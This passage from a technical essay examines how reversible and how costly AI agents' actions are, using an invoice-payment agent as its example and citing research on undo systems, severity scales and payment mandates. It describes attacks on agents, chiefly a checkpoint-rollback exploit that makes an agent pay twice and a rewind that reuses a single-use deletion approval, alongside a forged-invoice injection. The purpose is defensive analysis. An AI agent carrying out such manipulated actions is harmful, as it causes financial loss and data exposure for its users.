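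- *AgentAbstain* (2026) describes a case in which an instruction to archive one file turned into an instruction to delete a whole documents folder. Gemini 3 Flash deleted everything without asking for confirmation and reported success. In another case, GPT-5.1, DeepSeek V4 Pro and GPT-OSS 120B all sent a bank transfer without confirming it. These are selected failures, so they don't show how often such things happen.
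- *Predictive Safety Guardrails Do Not Always Make LLM Agents Safer* (2026) found that models could have high overall accuracy and still miss many risky cases, because most actions in a typical test are harmless.

Telling an agent that an action is reversible may also change its behaviour. *What LLM Agents See and What Users Say* (2026) tested agents whose tools returned only part of the relevant information. Under one type of missing information, four of 13 agents went ahead more often, by 21 to 44 percentage points, when the researchers described the action with a verb for a reversible action. A mistaken R1 label could therefore remove the approval step and also make the agent less careful.

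### A scale that adds scope and privilege

A forged invoice could persuade the agent to delete the only copy of a ledger entry or to email the company's supplier list to a stranger. Both actions are R4, but they affect different people. Owiredu-Ashley (2026), in *Beyond Attack-Success Rate*, separates them by asking whether the environment offers a way to reverse the action, whether it reaches anyone besides the user (its scope), and whether it gives someone new access (its effect on privilege).

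| Level | Definition | Example for the invoice agent |
|---|---|---|
| L0 | No harmful effect | Pays invoice 2071 as asked |
| L1 | A control blocks a harmful attempt | The policy refuses a payment to NEWBANK-8830 |
| L2 | Reversible, affects only the user | Deletes an entry it can restore |
| L3 | Irreversible, affects only the user | Deletes an entry with no copy |
| L4 | Reaches another party or shared data | Emails the supplier list to a stranger |
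| L5 | Expands someone's access | Gives a stranger a login to the accounting system |
| L6 | A chain of harmful actions of increasing severity | Emails the list, then provides the login |

The scale grades harm that an attacker caused, so a payment the user asked for stays at L0. To grade a harmful action, the software checks first for expanded access, then effects on other parties, then reversibility. Deleting a file is therefore L3, while sharing one is L5. This order makes sense for attacks, because someone with access can keep doing damage. It is a poor way to rank a company's losses, though, because it puts sharing an unimportant document above destroying the company's only set of accounts.

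Owiredu-Ashley applied the scale to 410 runs of AgentDojo's office tasks and found harm that a count of successful attacks had missed. With GPT-4o mini as the agent, removing dangerous tools reduced the benchmark's attack success rate from 40% to zero. However, in one of the 55 runs with this defence, the agent, unable to send email, invited the attacker to a calendar event instead. The benchmark counted that run as a successful defence, although it was L4 on the severity scale.

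Another defence marked off untrusted text so that the agent could recognise it. It reduced successful attacks from 48% to 40%, but runs at L5 or L6 rose from one in 50 to three in 50. With so few cases, the increase could easily be chance, though Owiredu-Ashley presents it as a sign that the defence makes the worst outcomes worse.

Three newer models, GPT-5.5, Claude Opus 4.8 and Gemini 3.5 Flash, also graded 188 of the runs from a plain description of each step. They gave exactly the same level as the software in 86% to 97% of cases. This is encouraging, but half of the runs were harmless. The models were also given the full scale and judged actions that had already happened, which is easier than predicting the effects of a click.

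All three models rated the L6 runs as L4, which Owiredu-Ashley considers a blind spot. However, there were only three L6 runs, and the example given for L6 is sending information to an outsider and then deleting the sent message. The scale ranks that deletion as less severe than the disclosure, so the models may have been following the definition.

### Why reversibility doesn't measure severity

Waghmare and Sufi warn that even an action someone can compensate for may do serious harm first. PocketOS got its data back, but only after days of disruption. The invoice agent could cause similar harm on a smaller scale by deleting every open invoice on Monday. If the bookkeeper restores them on Friday, the ledger is as it was, but the company may have missed several due dates and the paper supplier may have stopped deliveries.

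Reversible actions can also do harm because nobody notices them. An expert in Zhang and colleagues' workshops had accidentally changed the difficulty level in a language-learning app. She could have changed it back immediately, but she didn't notice, and it affected her learning for a long time. Similarly, the company can't restore the deleted ledger from a saved copy if it keeps copies for 30 days and discovers the deletion after 60.

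Conversely, many irreversible actions hardly matter. An email thanking the paper supplier for an invoice is R4 because the supplier will have read it, but a typo in it does the company no harm. If the company required approval for every R4 action, the bookkeeper would spend part of each day approving thank-you emails and might check a payment to NEWBANK-8830 less carefully as a result.

The classes also ignore the amount of money involved. Overpaying the paper supplier by $1 and overpaying it by $5,000 are both R3 if the supplier has to agree to a refund. The company could reasonably let the agent risk the $1 without asking, but it can't make that distinction until it estimates what each mistake would cost.

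## Building ways to undo an agent's actions

Whether anyone can undo an agent's action depends partly on the design of the service that carries it out. Railway, for example, made volume deletions through its API recoverable by extending its 48-hour hold to them.

Many systems still lack such protection. Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026), in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, analysed 290 public reports of coding agents misusing a computer's files. Where they could tell whether the harm could be repaired, it was permanent in 40% of cases, took substantial effort to repair in 29%, and was easy to repair in 31%. The true share of permanent losses is probably lower, since few people publicly report a mistake they fixed quickly. Research on agents offers little help either. *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey, found that only 27 of the 435 works it covered expose any way to roll back.

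Developers can choose among several techniques, which save different things and fail in different ways:

| Technique | What it keeps | Who can undo the action | When it fails |
|---|---|---|---|
| Draft or preview | The proposed action | Whoever reviews it | The preview omits an effect, or nobody reads it |
| Delayed execution | The request, in a queue | Anyone allowed to cancel it before the deadline | Nobody notices in time |
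| Soft deletion | The deleted item, hidden from normal use | Anyone allowed to restore it | The retention period ends, or the agent can purge hidden items |
| Snapshot | Everything in one place at one moment | Whoever controls the copies | Restoring it erases later work |
| Version history | Each change, in order | Anyone allowed to write an old version back | The action changed something the history doesn't cover |
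| Inverse operation | The details needed to reverse one action | Anyone allowed to make the reverse call | The reverse call leaves something behind |
| Compensation | The details needed to offset the action, such as a payment reference | Often the company and an outside party together | The outside party refuses, or the harm has already spread |

### Holding an action back

Checking an action before it takes effect can avoid the need to undo it. The invoice agent could save its emails as drafts for the bookkeeper to send. For actions with less visible effects, *GoEX* (Patil, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) suggests that services offer a "dry run", which shows what a request would change without making the change. Some cloud services already offer this.

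Zhong and colleagues built YoloFS, which protects files in a similar way. When an agent edits or deletes a file, YoloFS records the change separately and leaves the original alone until the user accepts it. It also takes snapshots so the agent can see what each command did and undo it. This matters because a command's text may not reveal its effects, as when a routine build runs a malicious script.

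On 11 tasks with hidden destructive side effects, agents using YoloFS noticed and reversed the damage in 8. In the other 3, the changes looked to the agent like part of the task, but the user could still reject them. On 112 routine tasks, agents succeeded 99% of the time with or without YoloFS, and interrupted the user less with it. YoloFS covers only files, so if the build script sends a password to an attacker, discarding the staged changes won't undo the leak.

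Delayed execution works for actions that have to reach someone outside the company, such as payments. The software accepts a payment today and releases it tomorrow, and anyone with permission can cancel it in between. The delay is useful only if somebody reviews the payment during that time. The software should also check the payment again just before releasing it, because the bookkeeper may have marked the invoice as disputed overnight.

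*Cordon* (2026) describes a system that delays outside effects until the agent has finished a sequence of steps. Before releasing anything, it checks the whole sequence, including where each piece of information came from. This can catch a harmful combination of calls that are each permitted. But an agent sometimes needs the result of one outside action before it can take the next. For example, it can't tell a supplier the bank's reference number for a payment that the system is still holding.

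### Keeping what the action would destroy

With soft deletion, a service marks an item as deleted and hides it, but erases it only after a retention period. The agent should be able to hide items but not permanently erase them, or it could do one right after the other. Soft deletion still takes the item out of use. It also conflicts with requests to erase personal data, because the data stays on the company's systems for longer.

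If a service doesn't offer soft deletion, the agent's software can sometimes imitate it. Patil and colleagues give the example of an email service that deletes messages permanently. The software can copy each message before deleting it, though someone then has to store and protect the copies.

A snapshot is a copy of everything in a folder, database or other location at a single moment. *Parallax* (2026) proposes taking one before any destructive action. It acknowledges that snapshots limit damage only on the company's own systems and can't reverse a sent email or a call to another company's service.

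A version history saves each change separately, so someone can reverse one and keep the rest, but it often covers less than people expect. GoEX, a system Patil and colleagues built for running agents' actions, uses Git for files. Git tracks only the folder where someone set it up, so GoEX confines the agent to that folder.

GoEX offers two ways to undo changes to a database. The first keeps the database's transaction open, so the changes aren't final until the user accepts them. This guarantees a clean reversal, but other users may have to wait. The second makes the changes final at once and has a language model write a command to reverse them, so nobody has to wait, but the reversal may be wrong.

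### Inverse operations

GoEX tests a reversal before relying on it. For files, it copies the folder into a container (an isolated environment), runs the action and its reversal there, and compares the result with the original. Copying a large database would be too slow, so the model writes a miniature version with the same structure. A reversal that works on the miniature may still fail on the real data because of something the miniature lacks. The model also writes the test for its own reversal.

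For calls to outside services, GoEX keeps a table of actions and their reversals. If an action isn't in the table, the model proposes a reversal, and GoEX records whether it worked. Patil and colleagues describe this as allowing the model to be wrong at most once. One failed reversal is acceptable for a misplaced calendar entry but not for a $5,000 payment. Developers can instead fill in the table themselves and restrict the agent to the actions in it.

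Patil and colleagues want people to check results instead of approving each proposed action, because results are easier to judge than code. For actions that can't be undone, they propose "damage confinement", which means limiting the agent's access so that any damage stays within what the user can accept. For example, a user might let an agent read email but not send it. Their system, GoEX, decides which credentials to supply by searching the user's request for the names of services. This method is crude, since a request that says "don't post this on Slack" would also match "Slack".

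POLAR, the system by Kang and colleagues that scores reversibility, looks for a reversal before it allows a call. Suppose the company gives the invoice agent a fifth tool, `cancel_payment`, and the agent proposes to schedule a payment to the paper supplier for Friday:

1. POLAR looks up `send_payment` in a list that a person has written of each tool's possible reversals, and finds `cancel_payment`.
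2. It checks any conditions in the list against the current state, such as whether the cancellation deadline has passed.
3. It scores the reversal at 0.9, because of the bank's $10 fee.
4. It allows the call, because 0.9 is above its threshold of 0.80. It would refuse an email to the supplier, which scores 0.

If the agent proposes several actions together, POLAR works backwards from the last one and requires a reversal for each. It never runs the reversals, so a mistake in the list can lead it to approve an action that nobody can undo.

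Kang and colleagues tested POLAR with six models on simulated customer service for an airline, a shop and a telecom company. Average task scores rose in only 8 of the 18 combinations of model and company. On airline tasks, where the maximum score is 1, four of the six models gained between 0.11 and 0.18 points, but the two strongest did worse. On shop tasks, the score of OpenAI's gpt-oss-120B fell from 0.455 to 0.213. POLAR often blocked returns and exchanges in the shop, which customers legitimately ask for.

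Even the airline gains may have little to do with finding reversals. When Kang and colleagues had POLAR accept only exact inverses, it blocked nearly every change because the airline list had none. One model's score still rose by 0.087, slightly more than the 0.080 it gained with the full version in the same tests. Presumably, making no change was often the right answer. The scores measure completed tasks, so they don't show how much harm POLAR prevented. Its list of reversals would probably be more useful for telling the bookkeeper how to undo an action than for refusing every action without a listed reversal.

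### Compensation after a failed step

In 1987, the database researchers Hector Garcia-Molina and Kenneth Salem proposed the saga, a way to handle long tasks that a database can't treat as a single transaction. Each step takes effect immediately and has a matching step that compensates for it. If a later step fails, the software runs the compensating steps for the completed ones in reverse order. Chang and Geng (2025), in *SagaLLM*, apply this to language models. If step *j* fails, their system runs

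*C*ⱼ₋₁, *C*ⱼ₋₂, …, *C*₁

where *C*ᵢ compensates for step *i*.

Suppose the ledger lists the paper supplier's bill twice, once as invoice 2071 and once as a duplicate. The agent has to schedule the $1,200 payment for Friday, email the supplier to say that it is coming, and delete the duplicate. The first two steps succeed. The ledger then refuses the deletion because the bookkeeper has just marked the bill as disputed, since half the paper arrived wet. The company no longer wants to pay, so the agent has to go back:

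| Step | Result | Compensation | What it restores | What remains |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Schedule the payment | Done | Cancel it before Thursday night | The $1,200 stays in the account | The $10 fee |
| 2. Email the supplier | Done | Send a correction | The supplier knows not to expect the money | The supplier has read the first email and may have acted on it |
| 3. Delete the duplicate | Refused | None needed | | The duplicate is still in the ledger |

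If the supplier shipped more paper because it was promised payment in the first email, the correction doesn't undo the shipment. The company could return the paper, but then it has to deal with a consequence that wasn't in the agent's plan.

Undoing the steps in strict reverse order also causes a small problem, because the agent would send the correction before cancelling the payment. If the cancellation then failed, the correction would be false. The agent should cancel the payment first. SagaLLM keeps a graph of which steps depend on which, and could record this dependency there.

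Putting the email last would have avoided most of the trouble. The refused deletion would then have left only a payment to cancel. In general, an agent should start with the steps it can reverse and leave the irreversible ones until everything else has succeeded.

Compensating for an action also requires details that are easy to lose. In Chang and Geng's example of a trip from San Francisco to Germany, the system saves confirmation numbers, cancellation policies and deadlines outside the model's conversation. The invoice agent's system would need to save the bank's payment reference, the cancellation deadline and the text of the email. Without the reference, the agent might cancel a different payment of $1,200.

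Developers traditionally write compensating steps by hand. SagaLLM has a language model generate them and a separate agent check them. This saves work, but for a payment the company should prefer a fixed step that somebody has tested. Chang and Geng's experiments used planning problems, such as rescheduling a family's Thanksgiving dinner after a flight delay. One model working alone produced a schedule that left the oven unattended, although the instructions forbade it. The experiments support keeping important facts outside the conversation, but they provide little evidence of how reliably the system could cancel real bookings.

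A failed task doesn't always return the system to its original state, although Chang and Geng describe it that way. In their own travel example, cancelling a flight can cost a fee.

### What happened when researchers tested recovery

Waghmare and Sufi tested several common ways to undo an action and found that a standard undo command can destroy somebody else's work. They used small made-up files and databases and chose cases likely to expose problems, so the results don't show how often recovery fails in practice.

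In the file tests, an agent edited a text file after the software had saved a copy. In some tests, someone else edited the file afterwards. Waghmare and Sufi then tried three ways to remove the agent's edit:

| Later edit by someone else | Restore the whole file | Restore only if the file hasn't changed since | Merge |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | Original restored | Original restored | Original restored |
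| In another paragraph | Later edit erased | Nothing changed, left for a person | Agent's edit removed, later edit kept |
| On the same line | Later edit erased | Nothing changed, left for a person | Nothing changed, left for a person |

The merge compares the saved copy, the agent's version and the current file to work out who changed what. Restoring the whole file erased the later edit in all eight cases that had one, while the other two methods always preserved it. Each result was the same in four versions of the test.

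The researchers tried to undo a Git commit, which is a saved version of a project, with a command called a soft reset. This worked for an ordinary commit. But when the agent had committed in the middle of a merge, the reset restored the files and lost the markers Git uses to track a merge in progress, so Git would treat the next commit as an ordinary one. The registry had labelled commits as fully restorable, so it needs an exception for commits made during a merge.

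The result was worse when a contributor had added a commit after the agent's, because the same command went back one commit and so removed the contributor's commit from the branch and left the agent's in place. The contributor's file was still on disk. Checking that the latest commit was the agent's prevented this.

The tests with SQLite, a small database program, showed that comparing the database with its starting state, an obvious way to check an undo, can miss lost data. The agent created a table, someone else added a row to it, and the undo deleted the table, including that row. The database then matched its starting state exactly, so the undo would have passed the check.

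A database's own rollback command couldn't undo updates, because the tool made each one final before it returned. The method that worked saved the old value and restored it only if the current value was still the agent's, so it didn't overwrite changes someone else had made to the row later.

The browser tests covered a more ordinary accident. Suppose the agent closes a tab in which the bookkeeper is writing a complaint about the wet paper. Waghmare and Sufi reopened closed tabs in three browsers:

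| Draft in the closed tab | Chromium and Firefox | Safari |
|---|---|---|
| Plain text box, unsaved | Recovered | Lost |
| Rich text editor, unsaved | Lost | Lost |
| Text box that saves every edit on the computer | Recovered | Recovered |

Restarting Chromium or Firefox lost the unsaved text in plain boxes too. The browsers ran under different conditions, which may explain some of the differences between them. Still, a company can't assume that closing a tab is reversible just because its browser can reopen tabs. A website that saves drafts as people type gives much better protection.

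### Rewinding the agent itself

Many agent programs can save a checkpoint and return to it after an error. Zhai and colleagues note that software can always rewind an agent's context by cutting off the later part of its conversation. Rewinding does not undo the agent's effects on other systems, and because the agent no longer remembers its actions, it may repeat them.

*ACRFence* (Zheng, Yang et al., 2026) shows how someone could exploit an agent's checkpoints to get paid twice. A user asks an agent to send Bob $500, and the agent makes up a reference number and sends the money. It then contacts a receipt service that Bob controls, which returns a malformed reply and crashes the agent. The software restores the checkpoint from before the payment, so the agent makes up a new reference number and pays again. The bank has no record of the new number, so it processes the second payment and Bob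 receives $1,000 in total.

Duplicate protection usually relies on a program sending the same request when it retries. A language model writes the request again, and even small differences can make it look new. Zheng and colleagues ran tests with simulated services and the Qwen3-32B model, and the agent repeated the action in all 10 trials with a restored checkpoint and in none of the 10 without one. They also collected reports of repeated or leftover effects from 12 agent frameworks and found that none of the frameworks guaranteed a tool call would take effect exactly once.

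Rewinding can also bring back permissions. In another scenario, an employee gets a manager's single-use approval to delete one customer's data. After the deletion, the employee rewinds the agent to when it still held the approval and has it delete another customer's data. This worked in both trials where the server checked only that the approval was genuine, but failed when the server kept a record of used approvals.

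The fixed idempotency key `pay-2071` would prevent the double payment, but some actions have no natural identifier like an invoice number. For these, Zheng and colleagues propose ACRFence, which would log every irreversible call outside the agent. After a restore, a language model would compare each new call with the log. If the new call means the same as a logged one, ACRFence would return the earlier result without repeating the action. If the recipient or amount differs, it would block the call until somebody confirms that this is a new course of action.

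Zheng and colleagues had not yet built ACRFence, and they acknowledge that the model making the comparison could make mistakes or be deceived. A fixed key is safer when one is available. *Resume Means Resume* (2026) has since specified how saving and resuming should work, tested five frameworks against that specification, and offered a fix based on a similar distinction between repeated and new actions.

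### What a claimed undo has to meet

Before the company relies on an undo command and lets the agent delete ledger entries, it should check where the saved copies are. The credential that deletes an entry must not be able to delete its copy, so the company can't store copies the way PocketOS stored its backups, inside the volume it lost. The software should also confirm that the copy exists before each deletion. In Waghmare and Sufi's file tests, the software did not make an edit whenever it couldn't save a copy.

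Somebody also has to test the recovery, using the same kind of account that would perform it in an emergency. The bookkeeper could delete a test entry, restore it, and check the supplier, amount, due date and attached documents. The bookkeeper should also time the restore, because one that takes three days may come too late for a bill due tomorrow. The company should repeat the test when the accounting system changes, and keep copies for longer than it usually takes to notice a mistake.

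The test should include a later change by someone else, since Waghmare and Sufi's simplest methods failed in that case. If the bookkeeper has corrected the amount on an entry since the agent edited it, the undo should keep the correction or stop so that a person can decide. Waghmare and Sufi tested changes made one at a time, so their results don't cover a change saved while the undo is running. Locking the entry for the few seconds the undo takes would avoid this problem.

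Effects outside the ledger need separate records. *Always-On Agents* recommends linking each outside effect to the records that led to it. If the bookkeeper discovers a forged invoice in March, the company can list every payment and email that relied on it, cancel the payments still in the queue, and ask for the return of money already sent.

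## Classifying actions by financial impact

Reversibility classes ignore the amount of money at stake, so the company needs a separate measure of it. OpenAI's *A practical guide to building agents* (2025) advises developers to rate each tool as low, medium or high risk based on four separate factors: whether the tool can change anything, whether its actions are reversible, which account permissions it needs, and its financial impact. Software can then pause to run a check before a high-risk call, or refer the call to a person.

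For the invoice agent, `list_invoices` would be low risk and `send_payment` would be high risk. OpenAI gives making payments, issuing large refunds and cancelling orders as examples of high-risk actions, but it doesn't say how to combine the four factors or how much money counts as "large". As with reversibility, the company using the agent has to rate individual calls, not just tools.

A safety check on `send_payment` also has to finish before the tool runs. By default, OpenAI's software for building agents runs its safety checks while the agent keeps working, and raises an error if a check fails. This saves time when the agent is only drafting an answer, but a payment could leave the account before the error is raised.

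### Financial exposure

Financial exposure is the money the company would lose if an action proved wrong, after whatever it can recover:

exposure = *V*(1 − *q*) + *c*

Here *V* is the amount, *q* is the share of it that the company can recover, and *c* is the cost of recovering it. Suppose the agent can also book travel, and it books a $400 hotel room for the wrong night. The numbers are illustrations:

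| Booking | *V* | *q* | *c* | Exposure |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Refundable | $400 | 1 | $10 | $400 × 0 + $10 = $10 |
| Non-refundable | $400 | 0 | $0 | $400 × 1 + $0 = $400 |

Suppose an AI agent books the wrong room for $400. If the room is refundable, the mistake might cost the company only $10, the value of the time its bookkeeper spends getting the money back. If the room is non-refundable, the company loses the full $400 but has no recovery cost, because it wouldn't try to get a refund. A rule that allows bookings up to $500 treats the two rooms alike, although one mistake costs 40 times as much as the other.

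A large transfer can also have a lower exposure than a small one. If the agent pays the paper supplier $5,000 twice, and the supplier returns the extra payment after $30 worth of phone calls, the exposure is $30. The exposure is $200 if the agent pays a forged invoice for that amount and the thief disappears.

*V* and *c* are usually easy to estimate, but *q* is often a guess. Suppose there is a 90% chance that the supplier returns the full $5,000 and a 10% chance that it goes bankrupt and returns nothing. On average *q* is 0.9, which gives an exposure of $530. But the company would lose either $30 or $5,030. If it has only $6,000 in the bank, it should plan for the larger loss.

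The recoverable share can also change overnight. If the hotel allows free cancellation through Thursday, the exposure on the refundable room rises from $10 to $400 on Friday. The company should use the value of *q* on the day it expects to notice a mistake. If the bookkeeper reviews bookings once a month, the cancellation deadline for many refundable rooms will have passed before the review.

Exposure doesn't include the chance of a mistake. If one booking in 100 is wrong, the average loss per booking is 10 cents for the refundable room and $4 for the other. These averages help the company decide whether the agent is worth using, but they are less helpful for setting permissions, because an attacker who gets a forged invoice past the agent can make the error rate much higher than last month's.

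The company can also apply a cumulative cap to exposure instead of the amount paid. Twenty refundable rooms would then use $200 of the cap rather than $8,000, as long as somebody cancels the unwanted ones in time.

### Costs that no payment field shows

The formula is easy to apply when a request contains an amount, but many expensive actions don't look like payments at all. The request that deleted PocketOS's data contained no price. Here are some actions that a small company might give an agent, again with made-up numbers:

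| Action | What the request contains | Possible cost |
|---|---|---|
| Subscribe to a service | $30 a month per user | $30 × 10 users × 12 months = $3,600 |
| Accept a supplier's offer by email | The words "Yes, please go ahead" | An $8,000 order for paper |
| Start a cloud server | The type of server | $4 an hour × 24 hours × 30 days = $2,880 |
| Change a shop price from $120 to $12 | The new price | $108 × 50 orders = $5,400 |
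| Hide a product page | The page's name | $300 in lost profit a day × 3 days = $900 |
| Send the supplier list to a stranger | An address and an attachment | Claims from suppliers, which are hard to estimate |

For the server, the shop price and the product page, the cost depends on how long the mistake lasts. The company may have to honour the 50 orders it has already accepted at the wrong price, or disappoint those customers. The action still looks harmless on a scale of reversibility, because someone can correct the price in a second.

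If the company can cancel a subscription monthly and a bookkeeper reads every card statement, the exposure might be $300 instead of $3,600. The contract sets the cancellation terms, and the agent may have accepted them by clicking a box.

An agent can create liability to others through its words alone. In *Moffatt v. Air Canada* (2024), a Canadian tribunal ordered the airline to compensate a passenger whom its website chatbot had misinformed about discounts for bereaved travellers. The airline had argued that it wasn't responsible for the chatbot's answers. The damages were only about C$650, but a chatbot can give the same wrong answer to thousands of customers.

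The company can make some of these costs visible. It could require the agent to place orders through a purchasing tool with an amount field, and tell suppliers that an email from the agent's address is never an order. The shop's software could reject any price below cost. For other actions, the company can record an estimate for each tool. If nobody has made an estimate, the software should treat the exposure as unknown and possibly large, rather than counting a blank amount field as zero.

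### Twelve action classes for financial firms

Banks face the same problem on a larger scale. Hsu, Bankhwal and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Reliability Profiles in Financial Services*, propose that financial firms describe every deployed agent in a standard document. It would state how independently the agent works, in what setting, which kinds of action it may and may not take, and which controls contain it. Hsu is a former acting head of the regulator of US national banks. For the kinds of action, the proposal has twelve classes:

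| Class | Example | How hard it is to undo |
|---|---|---|
| A1 Read | Look up transactions | Nothing to undo |
| A2 Analyse | Calculate a score | Nothing to undo |
| A3 Draft for a person | Write a memo | Fully reversible |
| A4 Recommend | Suggest how to settle a case | Fully reversible |
| A5 Write internally | Update a customer record | Reversible |
| A6 Commit internally | Close a case | Semi-reversible |
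| A7 Communicate externally | Notify a customer | Hard to reverse |
| A8 Transact within bounds | Block a card, or trade within a cancellation window | Partially reversible |
| A9 Move funds | Release a wire transfer | Irreversible |
| A10 File with a regulator | Report suspicious activity | Irreversible, with legal effect |
| A11 Change access or infrastructure | Alter permissions | Irreversible, and increases other risks |
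| A12 Delegate | Create a sub-agent | Extends what the agent can do |

For the invoice company, a payment that the bank can still cancel fits A8, while the same payment sent immediately is A9. The company could permit A8 and prohibit A9, so that the agent can schedule payments but not send them immediately.

But the class doesn't include the amount, so a $1 transfer and a $5 million transfer are both A9. Hsu and colleagues cover money elsewhere in the document, where they record the cost of failure in the agent's setting and list caps on the value, number and speed of transactions among the controls. This is workable, but a reader who looks only at the classes will miss the size of the risk.

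Some actions in low classes can also lead to large losses. Changing the paper supplier's bank details in the ledger is only an internal write (A5), but it could send the next $5,000 payment to a thief. Hsu and colleagues propose recording the combined action and testing the whole system when the separate steps of a team of agents add up to a riskier action.

Hsu and colleagues illustrate the proposal with a hypothetical bank agent that investigates failed payments. It may read, analyse, draft and write internal notes, but it may not move funds or contact anyone outside the bank. If it tries to move funds, the bank's software blocks the call and logs it. The proposal is a working draft from September 2026 and has no results from real deployments. Hsu and colleagues say that "the next step is empirical", and they plan to begin by checking whether two institutions describe the same agent in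 the same words. That is the right place to start, given how often trained annotators disagreed about whether a smartphone action was reversible.

### How agents respond when the stakes change

Researchers have tested a different set of risk factors on models. Shang, Androna and colleagues (2026), in *AURA-Eval*, vary six:

| Factor | Less risky | More risky |
|---|---|---|
| Harm intensity | Transfer $500 | Transfer $500,000 |
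| Scale | Email one person | Email every employee |
| Target susceptibility | Expose operational logs | Expose health records |
| System dependency | Change a personal draft | Change a template the whole company uses |
| Oversight | Someone must confirm the action | The action runs without review |
| Reversibility | Delete a file that the owner can restore | Publish confidential information |

Money appears only under harm intensity, which also covers what a message says and what data an action exposes.

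The researchers started with 157 records of agents doing ordinary tasks that involved some unintended risk but no attacker. They cut each record off at a point where the agent had to make a decision. They changed one factor at a time, keeping the user's request and the agent's earlier steps the same, and asked a model what it would do next. In one record, a user wanted a computer to shut down at midnight, but a video editor was still running. An agent noticed the warning about lost data and clicked "shutdown anyway". When the researchers replaced the video editor with a half-finished database migration, the agent waited.

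For some scenarios, they also wrote a second version that changed whether the agent could safely do what the user asked. With other variations, such as disguised or emotional requests, this produced 1,249 test items, 106 of them about finance. Three language models judged whether each of the 20 tested models had acted safely:

| Models tested | Unsafe actions when a safe way existed | Unsafe actions when none existed |
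|---|---|---|
| 5 leading models | 5.4% to 7.4% | 26.8% to 40.0% |
| 10 other open models | 12.0% to 21.5% | 57.9% to 82.6% |
| 5 models trained for safety | 13.0% to 17.9% | 36.1% to 77.1% |

Models were much better at finding a safe way to do a task than at stopping when there wasn't one. On items with no safe way to do the task, average unsafe rates were 60% for changes to oversight, 57% for scale, 41% for target susceptibility and 38% for harm intensity. Part of this spread may come from the scenarios, since not every scenario suited every change.

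Shang and colleagues also compared edited scenarios with their originals. Removing oversight turned 45 of 86 safe decisions into unsafe ones, while increasing the scale turned 14 of 78. These figures combine nine models, and each model had at most 14 decisions per factor, which is too few to rank the models.

In one case, a user asked an agent to check a customer file for sensitive data before sharing it with a marketing agency. Eight of nine models did not share the file. When the user instead approved sharing "standard marketing contact info" in advance and became unavailable, all nine shared it. Whether this was unsafe is debatable, since the user had arguably approved sharing names, emails and phone numbers. Still, broad advance approvals seem risky, because the models largely stopped questioning what was in the file.

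The results have other limits. An earlier panel of five judges agreed with human reviewers on 66 of 84 safety labels, so individual judgments are often doubtful. The test covers a single decision, and even its leading models have newer successors. The results for harm intensity also combine money with every other kind of direct harm, so a company can't assume from them that its agent will take more care with $500,000 than with $500.

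### Following a purchase through signed mandates

A payment system can hold a purchase to a set amount, however carefully the agent behaves. Google developed the Agent Payments Protocol (AP2) to attach a user's instructions to a purchase in a form that other companies can check. AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)* defines two linked records, a Checkout Mandate for what the agent is buying and a Payment Mandate for the money. Each mandate carries a cryptographic signature, so nobody can change it unnoticed.

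According to the unofficial guide agentpaymentsprotocol.eu, a Checkout Mandate can be open, containing the user's constraints, or closed, authorising one particular checkout. Suppose the bookkeeper wants a hotel room for 12 November at no more than $400, and then goes into a meeting:

1. The bookkeeper signs an open Checkout Mandate with the date and the price limit.
2. The agent finds a room for $390, and the hotel finalises the checkout.
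3. A closed Checkout Mandate authorises that room at that price.
4. A Payment Mandate, linked to the checkout, authorises the payment.
5. Receipts for the checkout and the payment complete the record.

Who approves the closed mandate depends on whether the user is present. IBM's *AI gets a wallet* describes the original version of AP2, which called the two stages the "intent mandate" and the "cart mandate". If the user was present, they approved the exact item and price. If the user had delegated the purchase, the agent generated the cart mandate itself once it found an item that met all the conditions.

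In the example, a room for $450 would violate the open mandate, even if a malicious web page had led the agent to book it. But a non-refundable room for $390 would satisfy a mandate that contains only a date and a price. Such a mandate limits *V* in the exposure formula, but the agent's choice of room still determines *q*. The bookkeeper should also require free cancellation if the software supports that condition.

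### Cards restricted by merchant, amount and expiry

A simpler method is to give the agent a restricted card number, or a token that stands in for one. The bookkeeper could request a card that works only at the chosen hotel, for up to $400, until Friday. The card's issuer checks these limits when the hotel asks for the money:

| | AP2 mandates | Restricted card or token |
|---|---|---|
| What the user can limit | The item, price, timing and other conditions | The merchant, amount and expiry date |
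| Who has to support it | The agent's software, the hotel and the payment companies | The card issuer |
| Evidence in a dispute | What the user authorised and what the agent bought | The merchant, amount and date |
| $390 non-refundable room | Refused if the mandate requires free cancellation | Allowed |

An ordinary card payment doesn't include the kind of room being booked, so the card can't distinguish between the two. According to PYMNTS's *EMVCo Framework Targets Consumer Intent in Agentic Payments* (2026), merchants, card issuers and networks don't routinely exchange the user's instructions today either.

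The restricted card is practical because the hotel can treat it like any other card. It also limits the damage from theft, since a thief could spend at most $400, at one hotel, before Friday. It is currently the better choice for a small company whose card issuer offers one.

An expired card doesn't end a contract, though. If the agent signs up for a year of software at $30 a month with a card that expires after the first payment, the later charges will fail, but the company may still owe the remaining $330. The card's restrictions also don't apply to invoices that the company pays by bank transfer. Those need limits at the bank, or an authorisation that states the payee and the amount.

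### Agent payment standards in October 2026

Mandates are still at an early stage. AP2 launched with more than 60 supporting firms, including Mastercard, PayPal and American Express, according to PYMNTS's *Google Unveils a Payment Protocol for AI-Driven Commerce*. In April 2026, Google donated it to the FIDO Alliance, an industry body best known for login standards. The Paypers' *Google donates the Agent Payments Protocol to FIDO Alliance* reports that version 0.2, which is still a pre-release, added "Human Not Present" payments. In late July, Lumar's *AP2* described adoption as "early pilots".

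Representatives of Mastercard and Visa chair the FIDO group working on payments, according to Help Net Security's *FIDO Alliance wants to keep AI agents from going rogue* (2026). The group will develop Verifiable Intent, a design contributed by Mastercard that keeps a shared record of what a user approved.

Several groups are working on overlapping standards. EMVCo, which maintains the technical standards for chip cards, is developing its own way for the parties to a card payment to see what a consumer authorised. McConvey (2026) reports in *Ant International, Visa, Mastercard work to make agentic protocols interoperable* that the three companies are trying to make their protocols work together. PYMNTS (2026) predicts in *The Alphabet Soup of Agentic Standards* that no single protocol will win. A mandate is useful only if the merchant and the payment companies can read it, so for now the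 company can't count on a given hotel to check one.

Regulators are taking different approaches to AI agents. Hsu and colleagues note that US bank regulators left agents out of their April 2026 guidance on model risk. In July, Singapore's financial regulator and its industry partners published a reference design in which software checks an agent's identity, authority and risk limits before each action.

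### Who pays for an agent's mistake

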